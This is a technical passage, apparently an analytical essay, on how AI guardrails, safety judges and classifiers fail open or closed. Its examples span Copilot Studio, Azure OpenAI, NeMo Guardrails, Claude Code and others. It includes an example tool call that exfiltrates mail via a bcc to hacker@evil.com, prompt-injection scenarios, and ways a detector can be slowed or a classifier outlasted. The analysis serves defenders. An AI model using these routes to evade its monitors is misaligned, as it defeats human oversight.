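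The issue was still open in July 2025, but two later releases addressed it. In version 0.6.0, OpenAI added a `run_in_parallel` setting for input guardrails. If the developer sets it to False, the guardrail has to finish before the agent starts, so a block prevents the model call and every tool call. Guardrails still run in parallel by default. Since version 0.8.0, the SDK cancels the model's task when a parallel guardrail finds a violation, which suggests that earlier versions could leave that task running.

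Cancellation limits the damage but can't undo a refund or an email that has already been sent. It also may not stop a tool that is already running. Since version 0.8.0, the SDK has run ordinary, non-asyncio tools in separate threads, and Python has no safe way to interrupt a thread from outside, so such a tool will finish even after the agent has been cancelled.

OpenAI recommends the blocking mode when starting the agent is too costly or risky, and the parallel mode when speed matters more than avoiding wasted work. Speed matters most in a chat, where a user notices an extra second before every answer. It matters much less for an agent that works for ten minutes, because an input guardrail runs only once, on the initial message.

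The blocking mode covers only part of the risk, because the input guardrail doesn't check instructions hidden in a web page that the agent opens later. Tool guardrails can check each call before it runs, but in the JavaScript edition they apply only to functions the developer has defined as tools. OpenAI excludes its hosted tools and the built-in tools for running shell commands, controlling a computer and editing files. An agent with the built-in shell tool could therefore delete files without a tool guardrail checking the command.

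The blocking mode also can't correct code that misreads the judge's verdict. OpenAI's JavaScript guide illustrates the mode with a judge that should stop requests for maths homework help. The sample code triggers the tripwire when `isMathHomework === false`, so it lets homework through and blocks everything else. Another OpenAI guide has the correct comparison, `=== true`.

### When one guardrail's error hides another's block

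The Agents SDK treats a judge error more strictly than the Guardrails library does. If an input guardrail raises an ordinary exception, the SDK passes it to the application instead of recording a result with the tripwire off. But as in the Guardrails library's strict mode, the error can hide another guardrail's block.

The SDK handles its guardrails' results in the order they finish. adityasingh2400 (2026), in *fix(run): cancel sibling guardrail tasks when one raises*, showed that when one guardrail fails immediately and another needs half a second, the application receives the error while the slower guardrail keeps running in the background. If that guardrail then finds a violation, the application never receives its verdict.

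The proposed fix, still a draft in May 2026, cancels the remaining guardrails when one fails. This avoids wasted work and stray side effects, but the application still gets no verdict from the slower guardrail. To be safe, the application has to stop on the error.

LangGraph, another agent framework, also cancels parallel work when a step raises an exception. In the forum thread *Interrupt parallel branch execution*, gui asked how a guardrail could stop an agent running beside it, and the answer was to raise a real exception in the guardrail's step. The agent was already streaming its output to the user, who might have read part of a forbidden answer before the block took effect.

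### Rejection and termination in Inspect

The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests advanced models, publishes an evaluation framework called Inspect. The framework distinguishes refusing an action from stopping the agent. Its 2025 versions sent certain expected tool errors back to the model, including timeouts, missing file permissions and ToolError, which a tool's author can raise on purpose. Other exceptions ended the sample (one attempt at one test task) with an error. A PolicyBlock raised inside a tool would therefore have stopped the agent unless it was derived from ToolError.

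Inspect also lets developers assign a person or program as an approver to review tool calls before they run. If the approver returns "reject", that call is refused, and the model is told and can continue. If it returns "terminate", the sample ends. Developers therefore don't have to rely on an exception raised inside the tool, which the tool's own error handling might catch. But if the termination is raised as an ordinary exception, a broad handler in the agent's code could still catch and suppress it.

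## Microsoft's one-second deadline and its content filter's error field

Developers who use an open-source guardrail library can read its code to find the handler that lets errors through, but customers of a hosted service have to rely on the provider's documentation and settings. In at least two services, Microsoft has had to decide what happens when a check fails. Copilot Studio, which companies use to build agents with little or no code, can have an outside security system check each tool call. Azure OpenAI, through which Microsoft sells access to OpenAI's models, filters the models' input and output text.

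### One tool call and one reply

Microsoft's release plan lists 4 September 2025 as the public preview date for Copilot Studio's external threat detection. An organisation can connect Microsoft Defender, another company's security product or a detector of its own. Copilot Studio receives only the detector's replies, so the detector may be a judge, a set of rules or a mixture. According to Microsoft's guide for administrators, the agent contacts the detector whenever it considers using a tool. Classic agents, which follow conversation paths laid out by hand, skip the check.

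Microsoft's guide for developers of detectors works through an example. A user asks an agent to email a customer and, when the agent asks which one, names John Doe. The agent looks up the address and plans to call its "Send email" tool. Before it does, it sends the detector the recent conversation, the outputs of earlier tools, its own reason for choosing this tool, a description of the tool and the values it wants to pass. Shortened, the last two parts look like this:

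```json
{
  "toolDefinition": {"name": "Send email"},
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  }
}
```

The user never mentioned the second address, which would receive a hidden copy, so the detector replies with `"blockAction": true` and can add a reason. To allow the call, it would reply with `"blockAction": false`. If it can't evaluate the request, for instance because a required field is missing, it returns an error object with no `blockAction` field. Unlike the twelve-line example, this interface separates errors from verdicts. Copilot Studio still has to determine what the agent does after an error.

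Neither of the two permitted verdicts lets a security product change the data in a tool call. CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, a guide to connecting its AIDR security product, explains that some AIDR rules normally alter the data they find. Because Copilot Studio accepts only a decision on the whole call, these rules report what they found and allow the call. A rule that masks card numbers elsewhere would therefore detect a card number in Copilot Studio but let it through.

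### What happens after one second

The detector has to reply in less than 1,000 milliseconds. Microsoft said when it announced the preview that if no response arrives in time, "the agent assumes approval and continues." Visual Studio Magazine's *Copilot Studio Adds Near Real Time Security Controls for AI Agents* (2025) described the deadline in nearly the same words, as did the independent analyst firm Directions on Microsoft (2025) two months later.

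The administrators' guide describes an option that the announcement left out. The "Set error behavior" setting controls what happens when a reply is late or an error occurs. Its default is "Allow the agent to respond", so Copilot Studio fails open unless an administrator changes the setting to "Block the query".

Microsoft's documentation leaves some doubt about whether "Block the query" applies to late replies. A note in the same guide says that the tool runs if no decision arrives within one second, without mentioning the setting, and the developers' guide also treats a late reply as "allow". Read literally, these passages would limit "Block the query" to error replies. They probably just describe the default, because CrowdStrike says that Copilot Studio applies the configured behaviour, allow or block, when AIDR misses the deadline. An administrator who relies on "Block the query" could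 check this by connecting a test detector that waits two seconds before answering.

Copilot Studio does catch some mistakes before an agent runs. It contacts the detector when an administrator saves the configuration, and the save fails if the address is wrong or the credentials don't work. A mistyped address therefore causes an immediate error message, unlike the mistyped model name in OpenAI's Guardrails library.

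This test covers only setup. Someone may delete the credentials a month later, or the detector may start to reject requests that it used to accept. For example, Microsoft tells developers that it may add fields to the request and that a detector should tolerate fields it doesn't recognise. A detector that accepts only the old format would return an error for every tool call after the change, and under the default setting all those calls would go ahead.

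### A late release and a new licence

The feature's general release has slipped at least once. A Microsoft notice reposted by itelio set it for 10 December 2025. By late June 2026, Microsoft's release plan listed it as "Jun 2026" without a day, and Microsoft adds the day only after a feature is out. *Copilot Studio*, an analyst's roadmap dated 28 June (Sanfilippo, 2026), still described Defender's monitoring of these agents as a preview. It is therefore unclear whether the feature was released in June as planned.

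The error behaviour has probably not changed. The CrowdStrike guide, which is undated but seems more recent than Microsoft's own pages, gives the same one-second limit and the same two options, labelled "fail-open" and "fail-closed". But this is only one vendor's description, and it doesn't include which option is the default.

A better-documented change on 1 July 2026 affects whether customers have a detector at all. Microsoft announced that from that day Defender's real-time protection for Copilot Studio agents would require a licence for Agent 365, its service for managing agents, and that customers without one would lose the protection. The same announcement also calls the protection "unchanged" for customers that continue to use it, which is hard to reconcile with a new licence requirement. *AI Features Cut from Defender for Cloud to Enhance Agent 365* (Miller, 2026) confirmed five days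 after the change that customers now had to license Agent 365 to get comparable features.

The announcement doesn't specify what Defender returns to an agent when the customer's licence has lapsed. If it returns an error or nothing, the default setting lets every tool call through, and the lapsed licence has the same effect as the renamed field in the twelve-line example. With "Block the query", the agents would stop at their first tool call, and someone would probably report the failure to IT that morning.

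Existing Agent 365 customers had a separate problem that did not involve a judge error. On 1 July, any of Agent 365's own protection rules that they had set to "Block" stopped blocking until an administrator defined them again on a new policy page. An administrator who missed the notice would have still believed the rules were in force.

### How a slow detector means fewer checks

A fixed deadline makes the number of checks depend on the detector's speed. The following figures are an illustration and don't come from any real detector. Response times on a network tend to cluster around a typical value, with a long tail of slow replies, and a log-normal distribution (one in which the logarithms of the times follow a bell curve) often describes them reasonably well. If *m* is the median response time in seconds and *σ* measures the spread, the share of replies that miss a one-second deadline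 is

P(T > 1) = 1 − Φ(ln(1/*m*) / *σ*)

where Φ(*x*) is the share of a standard bell curve that lies below *x*. With a median of 0.5 seconds and *σ* = 0.5, ln(1/0.5) is 0.693. Dividing by 0.5 gives 1.39, and about 8.3% of a bell curve lies above that point. So a detector that usually replies in half the permitted time still misses the deadline about once in twelve calls.

| Median response time | Replies that miss the deadline | Unchecked calls per 1,000 |
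|---|---|---|
| 0.3 seconds | 0.8% | 8 |
| 0.5 seconds | 8% | 83 |
| 0.7 seconds | 24% | 238 |
| 1.0 second | 50% | 500 |

Raising the median response time from 0.5 to 0.7 seconds nearly triples the share of calls that go unchecked, meaning they proceed without a verdict, though a person would barely notice the delay. Heavier traffic increases the number further. Suppose agents make 1,000 tool calls an hour at night and 2,000 in the morning, and the extra load raises the median from 0.5 to 0.7 seconds. Unchecked calls then rise from about 83 an hour to about 476, almost six times as many for twice the traffic.

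Once requests arrive faster than the detector can process them, the decline is much steeper. If a detector can handle 50 requests a second and 55 arrive, the queue grows by five every second. After ten seconds it holds 50 requests, so a new one waits a full second before the detector starts on it, and every reply from then on is late. The detector may be running at full capacity and reaching sound verdicts, but they arrive after the agents have stopped waiting. It can recover only if it discards expired requests or traffic drops.

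An attacker might also slow the detector with a very long web page, because the request includes the outputs of earlier tools. The risk depends on the detector. CrowdStrike's product analyses only the tool's name and input values and ignores the conversation history. This should make it harder to slow down, but it also prevents the product from comparing the planned action with what the user asked for.

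If a detector's median delay is 0.5 seconds and the delays are independent, choosing "Block the query" would stop about 58% of tasks with ten tool calls. An administrator with such a detector would do better to get a faster one. A small classifier would easily meet the deadline, but a judge that writes out its reasoning before the verdict probably would not.

### What the audit log records

An administrator needs a count of missed replies to notice any of this. Microsoft's announcement promised detailed audit logs of every interaction with the external system and suggested using them to evaluate that system's performance. Those logs would be the natural place to record missed replies.

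Microsoft's reference page on Copilot Studio's audit logs doesn't list such an entry. It lists events for creating, publishing, sharing and deleting agents, and one called `CopilotInteraction` for conversations with users. None of these events names the external detector, and none of the fields the page describes for Copilot Studio records the detector's verdict, its response time or a failure to answer. The log may contain more than the page documents, but an administrator can't tell from the documentation whether a tool call that went ahead after a timeout looks different from one the detector approved.

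The detector's log can be misleading too. Suppose it receives the request with the hidden copy to `hacker@evil.com`, takes 1.2 seconds and replies with `"blockAction": true`. Its log now shows a block, even though the agent began sending the email 200 milliseconds earlier. A security team can find such cases only by comparing the detector's response times with the deadline, or by matching its blocks against what the tools did. The request carries identifiers for the conversation and the step in the agent's plan, which should help with the matching. Neither method catches requests that never reached the detector.

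When Defender is the detector and blocks a tool call, it notifies the user and raises an alert for the security team, according to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*. If the company hasn't connected Defender to Microsoft 365, the blocking still works but the alerts don't appear. A week without alerts can therefore mean that there were no attacks, that Defender blocked attacks but the alerts didn't appear, or that its replies arrived too late to stop them.

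### A successful response that nobody filtered

Microsoft describes Azure OpenAI's content filter as an ensemble of classification models that examine both the prompt and the completion (the text the language model generates). The filter doesn't use a judge in the sense of a language model that writes a verdict. The same question arises when the classifiers are unavailable, and the customer's program has to find the answer in the response.

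A block on the prompt is easy to notice because the service returns HTTP error 400, "Bad Request", instead of an answer, and a client library normally turns a 400 into an exception. Microsoft's sample program catches the exception and prints a message that mentions the content management policy.

In documentation from 2023 to 2025, Microsoft stated that if the filtering system was down or couldn't finish in time, the request would still complete without filtering. This caused no exception, and the response had status 200 (success) and contained the model's answer as usual. The only sign of the failure was an error inside the `content_filter_results` object. Microsoft may have changed this since, so the current behaviour is worth checking.

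For an answer that the filter had examined and passed, the object looked roughly like this:

```json
"content_filter_results": {
  "hate":      {"filtered": false, "severity": "safe"},
  "self_harm": {"filtered": false, "severity": "safe"},
  "sexual":    {"filtered": false, "severity": "safe"},
  "violence":  {"filtered": false, "severity": "safe"}
}
```

For an answer that the filter had not examined, it looked like this:

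```json
"content_filter_results": {
  "error": {
    "code": "content_filter_error",
    "message": "The contents are not filtered"
  }
}
```

A program that only looks for violations treats the two objects alike. Suppose it checks whether `filtered` is true in each entry. None of the four entries in the first object meets that condition. The second object's only entry has no `filtered` field, so a program that tolerates missing fields also finds no violation and shows the text to the user. Like OpenAI's Guardrails library with its `execution_failed` field, the service records the failure, but an application has to check for it explicitly.

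Microsoft's sample program prints the model's message without reading the filter results, so it would print an unfiltered answer exactly as it prints a filtered one. That is reasonable for a demonstration of blocking, but a program built on the sample will also skip this check unless its developer adds it. The sample also catches every exception with the same handler, which prints the error message whether the network failed or the filter blocked the request. Only a person reading the message could tell which had happened.

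Under the behaviour that Microsoft documented, a caller had to distinguish four outcomes:

| What happened | HTTP status | What the caller has to read |
|---|---|---|
| The filter blocked the prompt | 400 | The error code `content_filter` |
| The filter cut off the answer | 200 | `finish_reason`, which is `content_filter` |
| The filter found nothing to block | 200 | Every category in `content_filter_results`, each with `filtered` set to false |
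| The filter did not run | 200 | The `error` entry in `content_filter_results` |

The status code settles none of these by itself. Three of the four outcomes share the code for success, and a 400 can also mean that the request was badly formed. The service reports on the prompt and the answer separately, so a careful caller reads both sets of results. A short function can sort each set:

```python
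CATEGORIES = {"hate", "self_harm", "sexual", "violence"}

def filter_status(results):
    results = results or {}
    if any(results.get(c, {}).get("filtered") for c in CATEGORIES):
        return "blocked"
    if "error" not in results and CATEGORIES <= results.keys():
        return "passed"
    return "not checked"
```

The function returns "passed" only if there is no error and all four categories are present. If there is an error, an empty object or a missing category, it reaches the last line and returns "not checked". This follows Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to base access on permission. The application can still show unchecked text, but it can now identify that text and count how often this happens.

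### When a filter's block turns into permission

A 400 status code from Azure OpenAI may be a policy block, but Copilot Studio treats a 400 from a detector as an error and lets the agent proceed by default. A company that combines the two services could therefore turn a policy block into an error and let the agent proceed.

Suppose the company writes its own detector and uses a model on Azure OpenAI as the judge. A stranger has planted instructions in a document, and as a result the agent plans to email a violent threat to a customer. The detector copies the planned email into the judge's prompt. Azure OpenAI's filter finds the threat and rejects the request with an HTTP 400 error, so the prompt never reaches the judge. The detector's code doesn't handle the resulting exception, so its web server returns an error to Copilot Studio, and under the default error setting the agent sends the email.

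A politer but equally harmful email would have passed the filter and reached the judge, which might have blocked it. To prevent the reversal, the detector has to recognise the `content_filter` error and return `"blockAction": true`. "Block the query" would also stop the email, along with every other tool call for which the detector returns no verdict.

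## Judges that answer without giving a readable verdict

A judge can reply on time and still leave the guardrail without a verdict. The guardrail relies on a parser, code that turns the judge's text into allow or block. A parser that finds no verdict can report an error, but many return allow or block anyway.

### From text to a verdict

Developers commonly use four methods, and the table gives an answer that breaks each of them.

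| Method | The judge's answer | What a careless parser does | Label |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search for the word "safe" | "Unsafe. The email contains a password." | Finds "safe" inside "unsafe" | Allow |
| Ask "Does this break the policy?" and compare the probabilities of "yes" and "no" | Two line breaks, then "Yes" | Compares them at the first line break, where neither word is likely | Arbitrary, possibly "allow" every time |
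| Read a field from JSON | `{"safe": "false"}` | Treats the text "false" as true, as Python does with any text that isn't empty | Allow |
| Let the judge write only "allow" or "block" (constrained decoding) | It would have written "I can't assess this" | Accepts whichever permitted word was more probable | Either |

The result of a keyword search can depend on the order in which it checks for words. *Context Over Content* (2026), a study of automated judges, checks for "unsafe" before "safe" because "unsafe" contains "safe". If it finds neither, it tries phrases such as "not safe". As described, however, a verdict line that reads "not safe" would already match "safe" in the first step, so the search would never reach those phrases. A search can also wrongly block harmless messages. One of NVIDIA's judges answers "harmful" or "unharmful", and a search for "harmful" would match both. The first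 test with a harmless message would at least reveal that fault.

The second method doesn't use the judge's written answer. A language model writes one token at a time and calculates a probability for every possible next token, so a program can compare the probabilities of "yes" and "no" directly. The program has to read them at the position where the answer appears. In *Unread or Unenforced?* (2026), one judge began its answers with two line breaks, so reading the probabilities at the first token gave a block rate of zero, even though that judge blocks almost everything. The study now reports the combined probability of the two labels. If it is far below one, the program is probably reading the wrong position.

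In *HiveTraceGuard-Pro*, Oblakov, Sadiekh and Kokuykin (2026) use this method for a small judge that labels messages "safe" or "unsafe". On 2,777 English inputs, the most probable token in the judge's vocabulary was always one of these two words, so the comparison never overlooked a more probable answer. But comparing two numbers nearly always produces a label, even when the judge hasn't seen the message. Oblakov et al. warn that software that shortens long prompts from the end would cut off the message to be judged. The program would still get "safe" or "unsafe" back.

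A program can check a JSON answer against a schema, which describes the required fields and their permitted values. This check would reject the text "false" where the schema requires a true-or-false value, as well as the renamed field and the unexpected "deny" from the twelve-line example. The guardrail can then at least detect an error. Strict checks also reject some answers that a person could easily read, such as correct JSON inside the formatting marks that models often put around code. According to LiteLLM's *LLM-as-a-Judge*, the documentation for a judge built into a gateway between applications and model providers, that judge's parser accepts JSON with these marks.

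Some programs try several ways of reading a verdict. *BioFirewall* (2026), a system that screens the work of agents designing genetic sequences, first looks for JSON. If that fails, it searches the text for "refuse", "flag" and "allow", in that order, so "I see no reason to refuse" counts as a refusal, which is wrong but cautious. The program records that it has no verdict only if both attempts fail.

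Constrained decoding prevents most format errors. At each step, the software that runs the judge rules out every token that would break the schema, so a finished answer always fits it. An answer can still hit the length limit before it is finished. And a judge that can't assess a message can't report that unless the developer adds a third permitted value, such as "cannot assess".

### What NeMo Guardrails makes of an unreadable answer

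NeMo Guardrails is an open-source library from NVIDIA that works with judges from several companies. The developer chooses a parser for each judge. The reference page NVIDIA's *nemoguardrails.llm.output_parsers* describes three kinds:

- `is_content_safe` looks for keywords. "Safe" or "no" means safe, and "unsafe" or "yes" means unsafe.
- Two parsers read the JSON that NVIDIA's own content-safety judge returns.
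- Two more look for lines such as "Prompt harm: unharmful", which a judge that reasons before it answers produces.

The function that extracts the reasoning judge's value returns "harmful" if parsing fails. If the answer is empty, the check logs a warning and continues with the empty text, "which the parser typically treats as unsafe", according to NVIDIA's *Content Safety*. NeMo Guardrails thus tends to fail closed on an unreadable answer. Exceptions are possible because developers can register their own parsers, and NVIDIA lists no rule for what `is_content_safe` does with an answer that contains none of its four keywords. OpenAI's library, by contrast, lets the request continue after an error.

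When the parser can't read the judge's verdict, LiteLLM logs a warning and lets the content through, whereas NeMo Guardrails blocks it. LiteLLM keeps better records of these cases because it gives them their own status, `guardrail_failed_to_respond`. The parser in NeMo Guardrails returns only whether the content is safe and, for some judges, which rules it broke. A user whose harmless question gets an unreadable verdict therefore sees the same refusal as someone who asked for a bomb recipe.

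In version 0.18.0 of the library, such an error could also outlast the request. NVIDIA's code can store the result of each check and reuse it when the same message comes again, which saves a call to the judge. It does this even when the judge's answer was unreadable, so a harmless message that was blocked once would stay blocked while the result remained in storage.

A cautious default can also become permissive if later code reverses it. The library uses `is_content_safe` to check facts too, where "yes" means the text is fine, so the fact check reverses the parser's result. If the parser can't read the answer and falls back on "unsafe", the reversal would turn that into a pass.

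A low output limit can also cut off the verdict. Version 0.18.0 allowed the judge three tokens unless the developer set another limit. That is enough for "Yes" or "unsafe", but not for JSON or for a judge that reasons before answering, so NVIDIA's setup instructions for the JSON judge raise the limit to 50. The default is now 1,024. An NVIDIA example for reasoning judges uses 2,048, but the company's tutorial for one such judge, *Content Safety with Nemotron-Content-Safety-Reasoning-4B*, sets only 400.

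A longer answer gives a keyword parser more text to misread. NVIDIA's sample prompt for ShieldGemma, Google's safety judge, calls for "Yes" or "No" followed by a step-by-step explanation. If the judge writes "No. The user wants to know how to spot unsafe wiring," the answer contains both "no" and "unsafe". With a three-token limit, the parser would receive little more than the "No". If it searches the whole answer, the label depends on which keyword it tests first.

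### How often judges return no usable verdict

Few studies of safety judges report this rate. Two from September 2026 do, both in an appendix.

In *AdaGuard*, Feng, Ding and colleagues (2026) tested thirteen models on 1,000 records, mostly of agents at work. Half of the records broke a written policy. Eight of the models returned invalid answers, and the table shows five of those eight. Feng and colleagues counted every invalid answer as wrong. The last column shows what the accuracy would have been if they had dropped those answers instead.

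| Model | Invalid answers out of 1,000 | Published accuracy | Accuracy without the invalid answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 2 | 76.1% | 76.3% |
| AdaGuard-8B | 8 | 89.5% | 90.2% |
| DynaGuard-4B | 20 | 67.3% | 68.7% |
| Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite | 103 | 72.1% | 80.4% |
| YuFeng-XGuard-Reason-8B | 139 | 57.3% | 66.6% |

A guardrail that needs only allow or block could have read some of these invalid answers. Gemini had to list the broken rules in the policy's order, and Feng and colleagues treated a correct list in the wrong order as invalid. Gemini gave no invalid answers on a second test with 543 examples, so the strict format is probably the main reason for its 103 invalid answers. YuFeng-XGuard only had to choose between two options, yet it gave 36 invalid answers, or 6.6%, on the second test.

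Oblakov and colleagues ran 35 judges on 44 datasets and dropped every item for which a judge gave no usable verdict. Most judges answered almost every item. Of the 1,540 combinations of judge and dataset, one had no score and 81 others were missing some verdicts. On one set of 852 model responses, two NVIDIA judges failed on 36 and 39 items (4.2% and 4.6%), while the other thirteen judges in the main comparison answered all 852. In the worst case, a judge gave no usable verdict on 421 of 1,709 items (24.6%). A low average failure rate across all judges would therefore be a poor guide to any one judge's rate, so a team would have to measure its own judge on its own traffic.

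A judge trained to use a format may still fail to use it. *Aletheia* (2026) studied models that judge code and must put their choice in a marked box. Most did so nearly every time, but one with 1.5 billion parameters gave a readable verdict in only 43% of its answers because it often kept writing without finishing.

A program can bring the rate of unreadable verdicts down to zero by adding fallback methods for reading answers. *Context Over Content* reports a label for all 18,240 of its judgments, with a second language model, GPT-4o-mini, available as a last resort for answers that simpler methods couldn't read. But when an answer has no clear verdict, the label partly reflects the fallback model's decision instead of the judge's. In *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model* (2026), three language models read other models' analyses of possibly vulnerable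 code. About 5,200 of these analyses had no verdict line. The three models labelled nearly all of them, but the share labelled "vulnerable" ranged from 44% to 57% depending on which model read them.

### How the scoring rule changes the result

Buyers usually compare judges by accuracy, and the ranking can depend on how invalid answers are treated. GPT-5.2 leads Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite by four points in the published figures but trails it by four when invalid answers are excluded.

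Oblakov and colleagues acknowledge that dropping invalid answers can raise a judge's score or leave it unchanged, but never lower it. Suppose the judge that gave no readable verdict on 421 of 1,709 items was right on 90% of the rest. Its reported accuracy would be 90%, but it would be 68% if the missing verdicts counted as errors.

Feng and colleagues chose a stricter rule, but it doesn't match any real guardrail. It counts an invalid answer as a missed violation on a harmful item, as if the guardrail failed open, and as a false alarm on a harmless item, as if it failed closed. A real guardrail makes only one of these mistakes, so the published accuracy is the lowest possible. For Gemini, the true figure would lie between 72.1% and 82.4%, depending on how the guardrail treats errors and how many of the 103 invalid answers fell on harmful items. If half did, accuracy would be about 77% whether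 the guardrail failed open or closed.

*BioFirewall* uses more than one rule for answers without a readable verdict. One experiment counts an unreadable answer as a failure to flag the item, which lowers the detection rate. If the judge refuses to engage with an item, that experiment leaves the item out of both the detection rate and the false-alarm rate. *BioFirewall* cautions that a low detection rate may partly reflect unreadable answers.

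If a benchmark counts errors as safe, a model can get a perfect score without being tested. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* (2026) examined ASB, a benchmark that attacks agents and records each attack as either a success or a failure. Two of the models rejected all 400 requests because they didn't accept the format of ASB's messages, so ASB reported an attack success rate of 0% for them. One defence seemed to make no difference because some of its runs had failed and ASB had scored them as secure. On the 320 cases that reached the model every time, the defence raised attack success from 30.3% to 35.6%.

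Counting an unreadable verdict as a tie between the two candidates is another way to hide the problem. One measure in *Aletheia* does this, and the judge that answered readably only 43% of the time scored rather well on it. The same judge did worse than random guessing on a measure that counted its unreadable verdicts as failures.

### Why errors may cluster on harmful items

An overall error rate of 2% is reassuring only if errors are equally common on harmless and harmful items, and there is reason to doubt that they are.

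The judge may refuse to assess the item. Developers train general-purpose models to decline harmful requests, and a judge's prompt contains the text it must assess. BioFirewall had to count such refusals separately. The provider may also reject the request before it reaches the judge, as Azure OpenAI's filter does with the threatening email in the earlier example. *EviSafe* (2026), a safety benchmark for models that read images, retries requests after temporary failures but doesn't keep retrying those that fail a provider's content inspection. This is sensible because the same text would probably fail again, but retries therefore do little for the errors most closely tied to harmful content.

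The judge may also reach its token limit before it finishes answering. NVIDIA's JSON judge has to list the categories that a message violates, but its prompt tells it to omit the list if everything is safe. A message that breaks several rules therefore needs a longer answer than a harmless one, and that answer is more likely to hit the 50-token limit. A reasoning judge may need more tokens for a difficult case than for a simple greeting. Longer answers also take more time, so they are more likely to miss a deadline like Copilot Studio's. An adversary may also try to cause judge errors.

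It is unclear how strong the effect is in practice, because neither Feng and colleagues nor Oblakov and colleagues publish separate counts of invalid answers for harmful and harmless items. For YuFeng-XGuard, though, other figures in *AdaGuard* give a range. The model was wrong on only 72 of the 500 harmless records, including any invalid answers, so at least 67 of its 139 invalid answers must have been on harmful records. That means it gave invalid answers on between 13% and 28% of harmful records, compared with 14% of all 1,000 records. The low end would mean almost no clustering, and the high end would mean that every invalid answer was on a harmful record.

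### What gets through and what gets stopped

A short calculation shows how much clustering matters. Let *r* be the share of harmful items that the judge detects when it gives a verdict, and *e* the share of harmful items on which it gives none. The judge then returns a verdict on 1 − *e* of the harmful items and blocks *r*(1 − *e*) of them. If the guardrail fails open, everything else passes:

harmful items that pass = 1 − *r*(1 − *e*)

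If it fails closed, an item passes only when the judge returns a verdict and that verdict is wrong:

harmful items that pass = (1 − *r*)(1 − *e*)

The difference between the two is exactly *e*. The table assumes a judge that detects 95% of harmful items when it gives a verdict.

| Errors on harmful items (*e*) | Harmful items that pass if the guardrail fails open | Harmful items that pass if it fails closed |
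|---|---|---|
| 0% | 5.0% | 5.0% |
| 2% | 6.9% | 4.9% |
| 10% | 14.5% | 4.5% |
| 30% | 33.5% | 3.5% |

In the last row, the judge gives a verdict on 700 of 1,000 harmful items, blocking 665 and missing 35. The other 300 get no verdict. A guardrail that fails closed stops these 300, but one that fails open lets them through along with the 35 misses. In that case 335 harmful items pass, about a third of the total, even though the judge's advertised detection rate is 95%.

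The right-hand column falls as errors rise because a guardrail that fails closed blocks every item on which its judge errors. A team that tracks only how many harmful items get through could therefore think a failing judge is improving.

Whether a published detection rate can be used as *r* depends on how the study scored invalid answers. If the study dropped them, the rate is *r*. If it counted them as misses, as Feng and colleagues did, the rate is already *r*(1 − *e*), and one minus that rate is the share that passes when the guardrail fails open. For Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite, with a published detection rate of 65.4%, that share is 34.6%.

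Failing closed blocks more harmless items than failing open. If the judge returns no readable verdict on 2% of harmless items and wrongly blocks 1% of the rest, a guardrail that fails closed stops 0.02 + 0.98 × 0.01, or about 3%, of harmless items, while one that fails open stops just under 1%.

Whether failing closed is worth it depends on how common harmful messages are and whether the judge errs more often on them. Suppose a service handles 10,000 messages a day, ten of them harmful. If the judge errs on 2% of all messages, failing closed stops one extra harmful message every five days and about 200 extra harmless ones every day. If the error rate is instead 30% on harmful messages and still 2% on harmless ones, failing closed stops three extra harmful messages a day and the same number of harmless ones as before.

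## Claude Code, where the classifier fails closed and hooks fail open

Claude Code is Anthropic's coding agent, which edits files and runs commands on a programmer's computer. Two kinds of guardrail can stop those actions. The built-in auto mode sends risky actions to a judge model and normally holds an action back if the judge returns no verdict. Hooks are check scripts that users write, and when one crashes, the action usually goes ahead.

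In Manual mode, Claude Code asks the user before most actions that edit files, run commands or reach the network. In auto mode a second model, which Anthropic calls the classifier, decides instead. Auto mode became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans in August 2026, and later for terminal sessions on every plan.

Most actions never reach the classifier. Claude Code first applies the user's own rules, which can allow a command, forbid it or require Claude Code to ask first. It then approves read-only actions and most edits inside the project folder. Nearly everything else goes to the classifier. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the text those tools return, so instructions planted in a web page can't reach it directly.

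Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier with two stages. The first is a fast filter that outputs a single yes-or-no token and errs on the side of blocking. If it flags an action, the second stage runs the model again, this time with reasoning before the verdict. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's staff, the second stage cut the share of harmless actions blocked from 8.5% to 0.4%. On 52 real actions in which Claude had gone further than the user allowed, the two stages together missed 17%. The classifier ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 at the time and now runs on Sonnet 5 by default, so the current rates may differ.

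If 0.4% of harmless actions are wrongly blocked and the errors are independent, a session with 200 harmless checked actions has a 55% chance of at least one wrong block. A block therefore doesn't end the session. Claude receives the reason for the block as the result of its tool call and looks for a safer way to continue, so a wrong block usually means just one retry.

### What happens to the action

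The table is based on Anthropic's error reference and its page on permission modes as of November 2026. The pause in the last column begins when the classifier has blocked three actions in a row or 20 in total.

| Outcome | Does the action run? | Message to Claude | Counts toward the pause? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Genuine block | No | The reason, usually the name of the rule | Yes |
| Classifier unavailable | No | The model is temporarily unavailable, with a cause if known | Not stated |
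| Unparseable response | No | A message for this kind of failure | Not stated |
| Separate safety check refuses the classifier's request | No | This is no judgment on the action; go on with other tasks | No |
| Conversation too long to check | Only if the user approves it | The action was not reviewed and did not run | Not stated |
| No verdict from the server | No | No verdict, with a cause if known and whether one retry can help | Not stated; has its own limit of ten responses |

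While auto mode is paused, Claude Code asks the user about each action, as it would in Manual mode. Auto mode resumes when the user approves one. Users can't change the two limits, which Anthropic describes as a backstop against an agent that keeps pushing towards something the user wouldn't want.

A programmer can start an unattended run with `claude -p`, for example from an overnight script. Claude Code used to end such a run when it reached a limit on blocked actions. According to the current documentation, the blocked action doesn't run but Claude keeps working. This avoids losing a night's work to a few wrong blocks, but it also gives a misdirected agent more attempts. With a 17% miss rate and independent attempts, a forbidden action would get through within three tries 43% of the time and within ten tries 84% of the time. Real attempts probably aren't independent, since the classifier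 tends to repeat a mistake about what the user agreed to, but the limit clearly offers less protection in an unattended run than it used to.

When the classifier is unavailable, the error message may give the cause as rate-limited, overloaded, server error, timed out or connection failed. Claude usually retries automatically, but some causes persist. A company that reaches Claude through Amazon Bedrock, Amazon's service for hosted models, may not have access to the classifier's model, or a user may have chosen a classifier model that the provider doesn't serve. Claude Code then blocks every action that needs the classifier and includes the model's name in the error message, whereas a mistyped model name in OpenAI's Guardrails library lets every message through unchecked.

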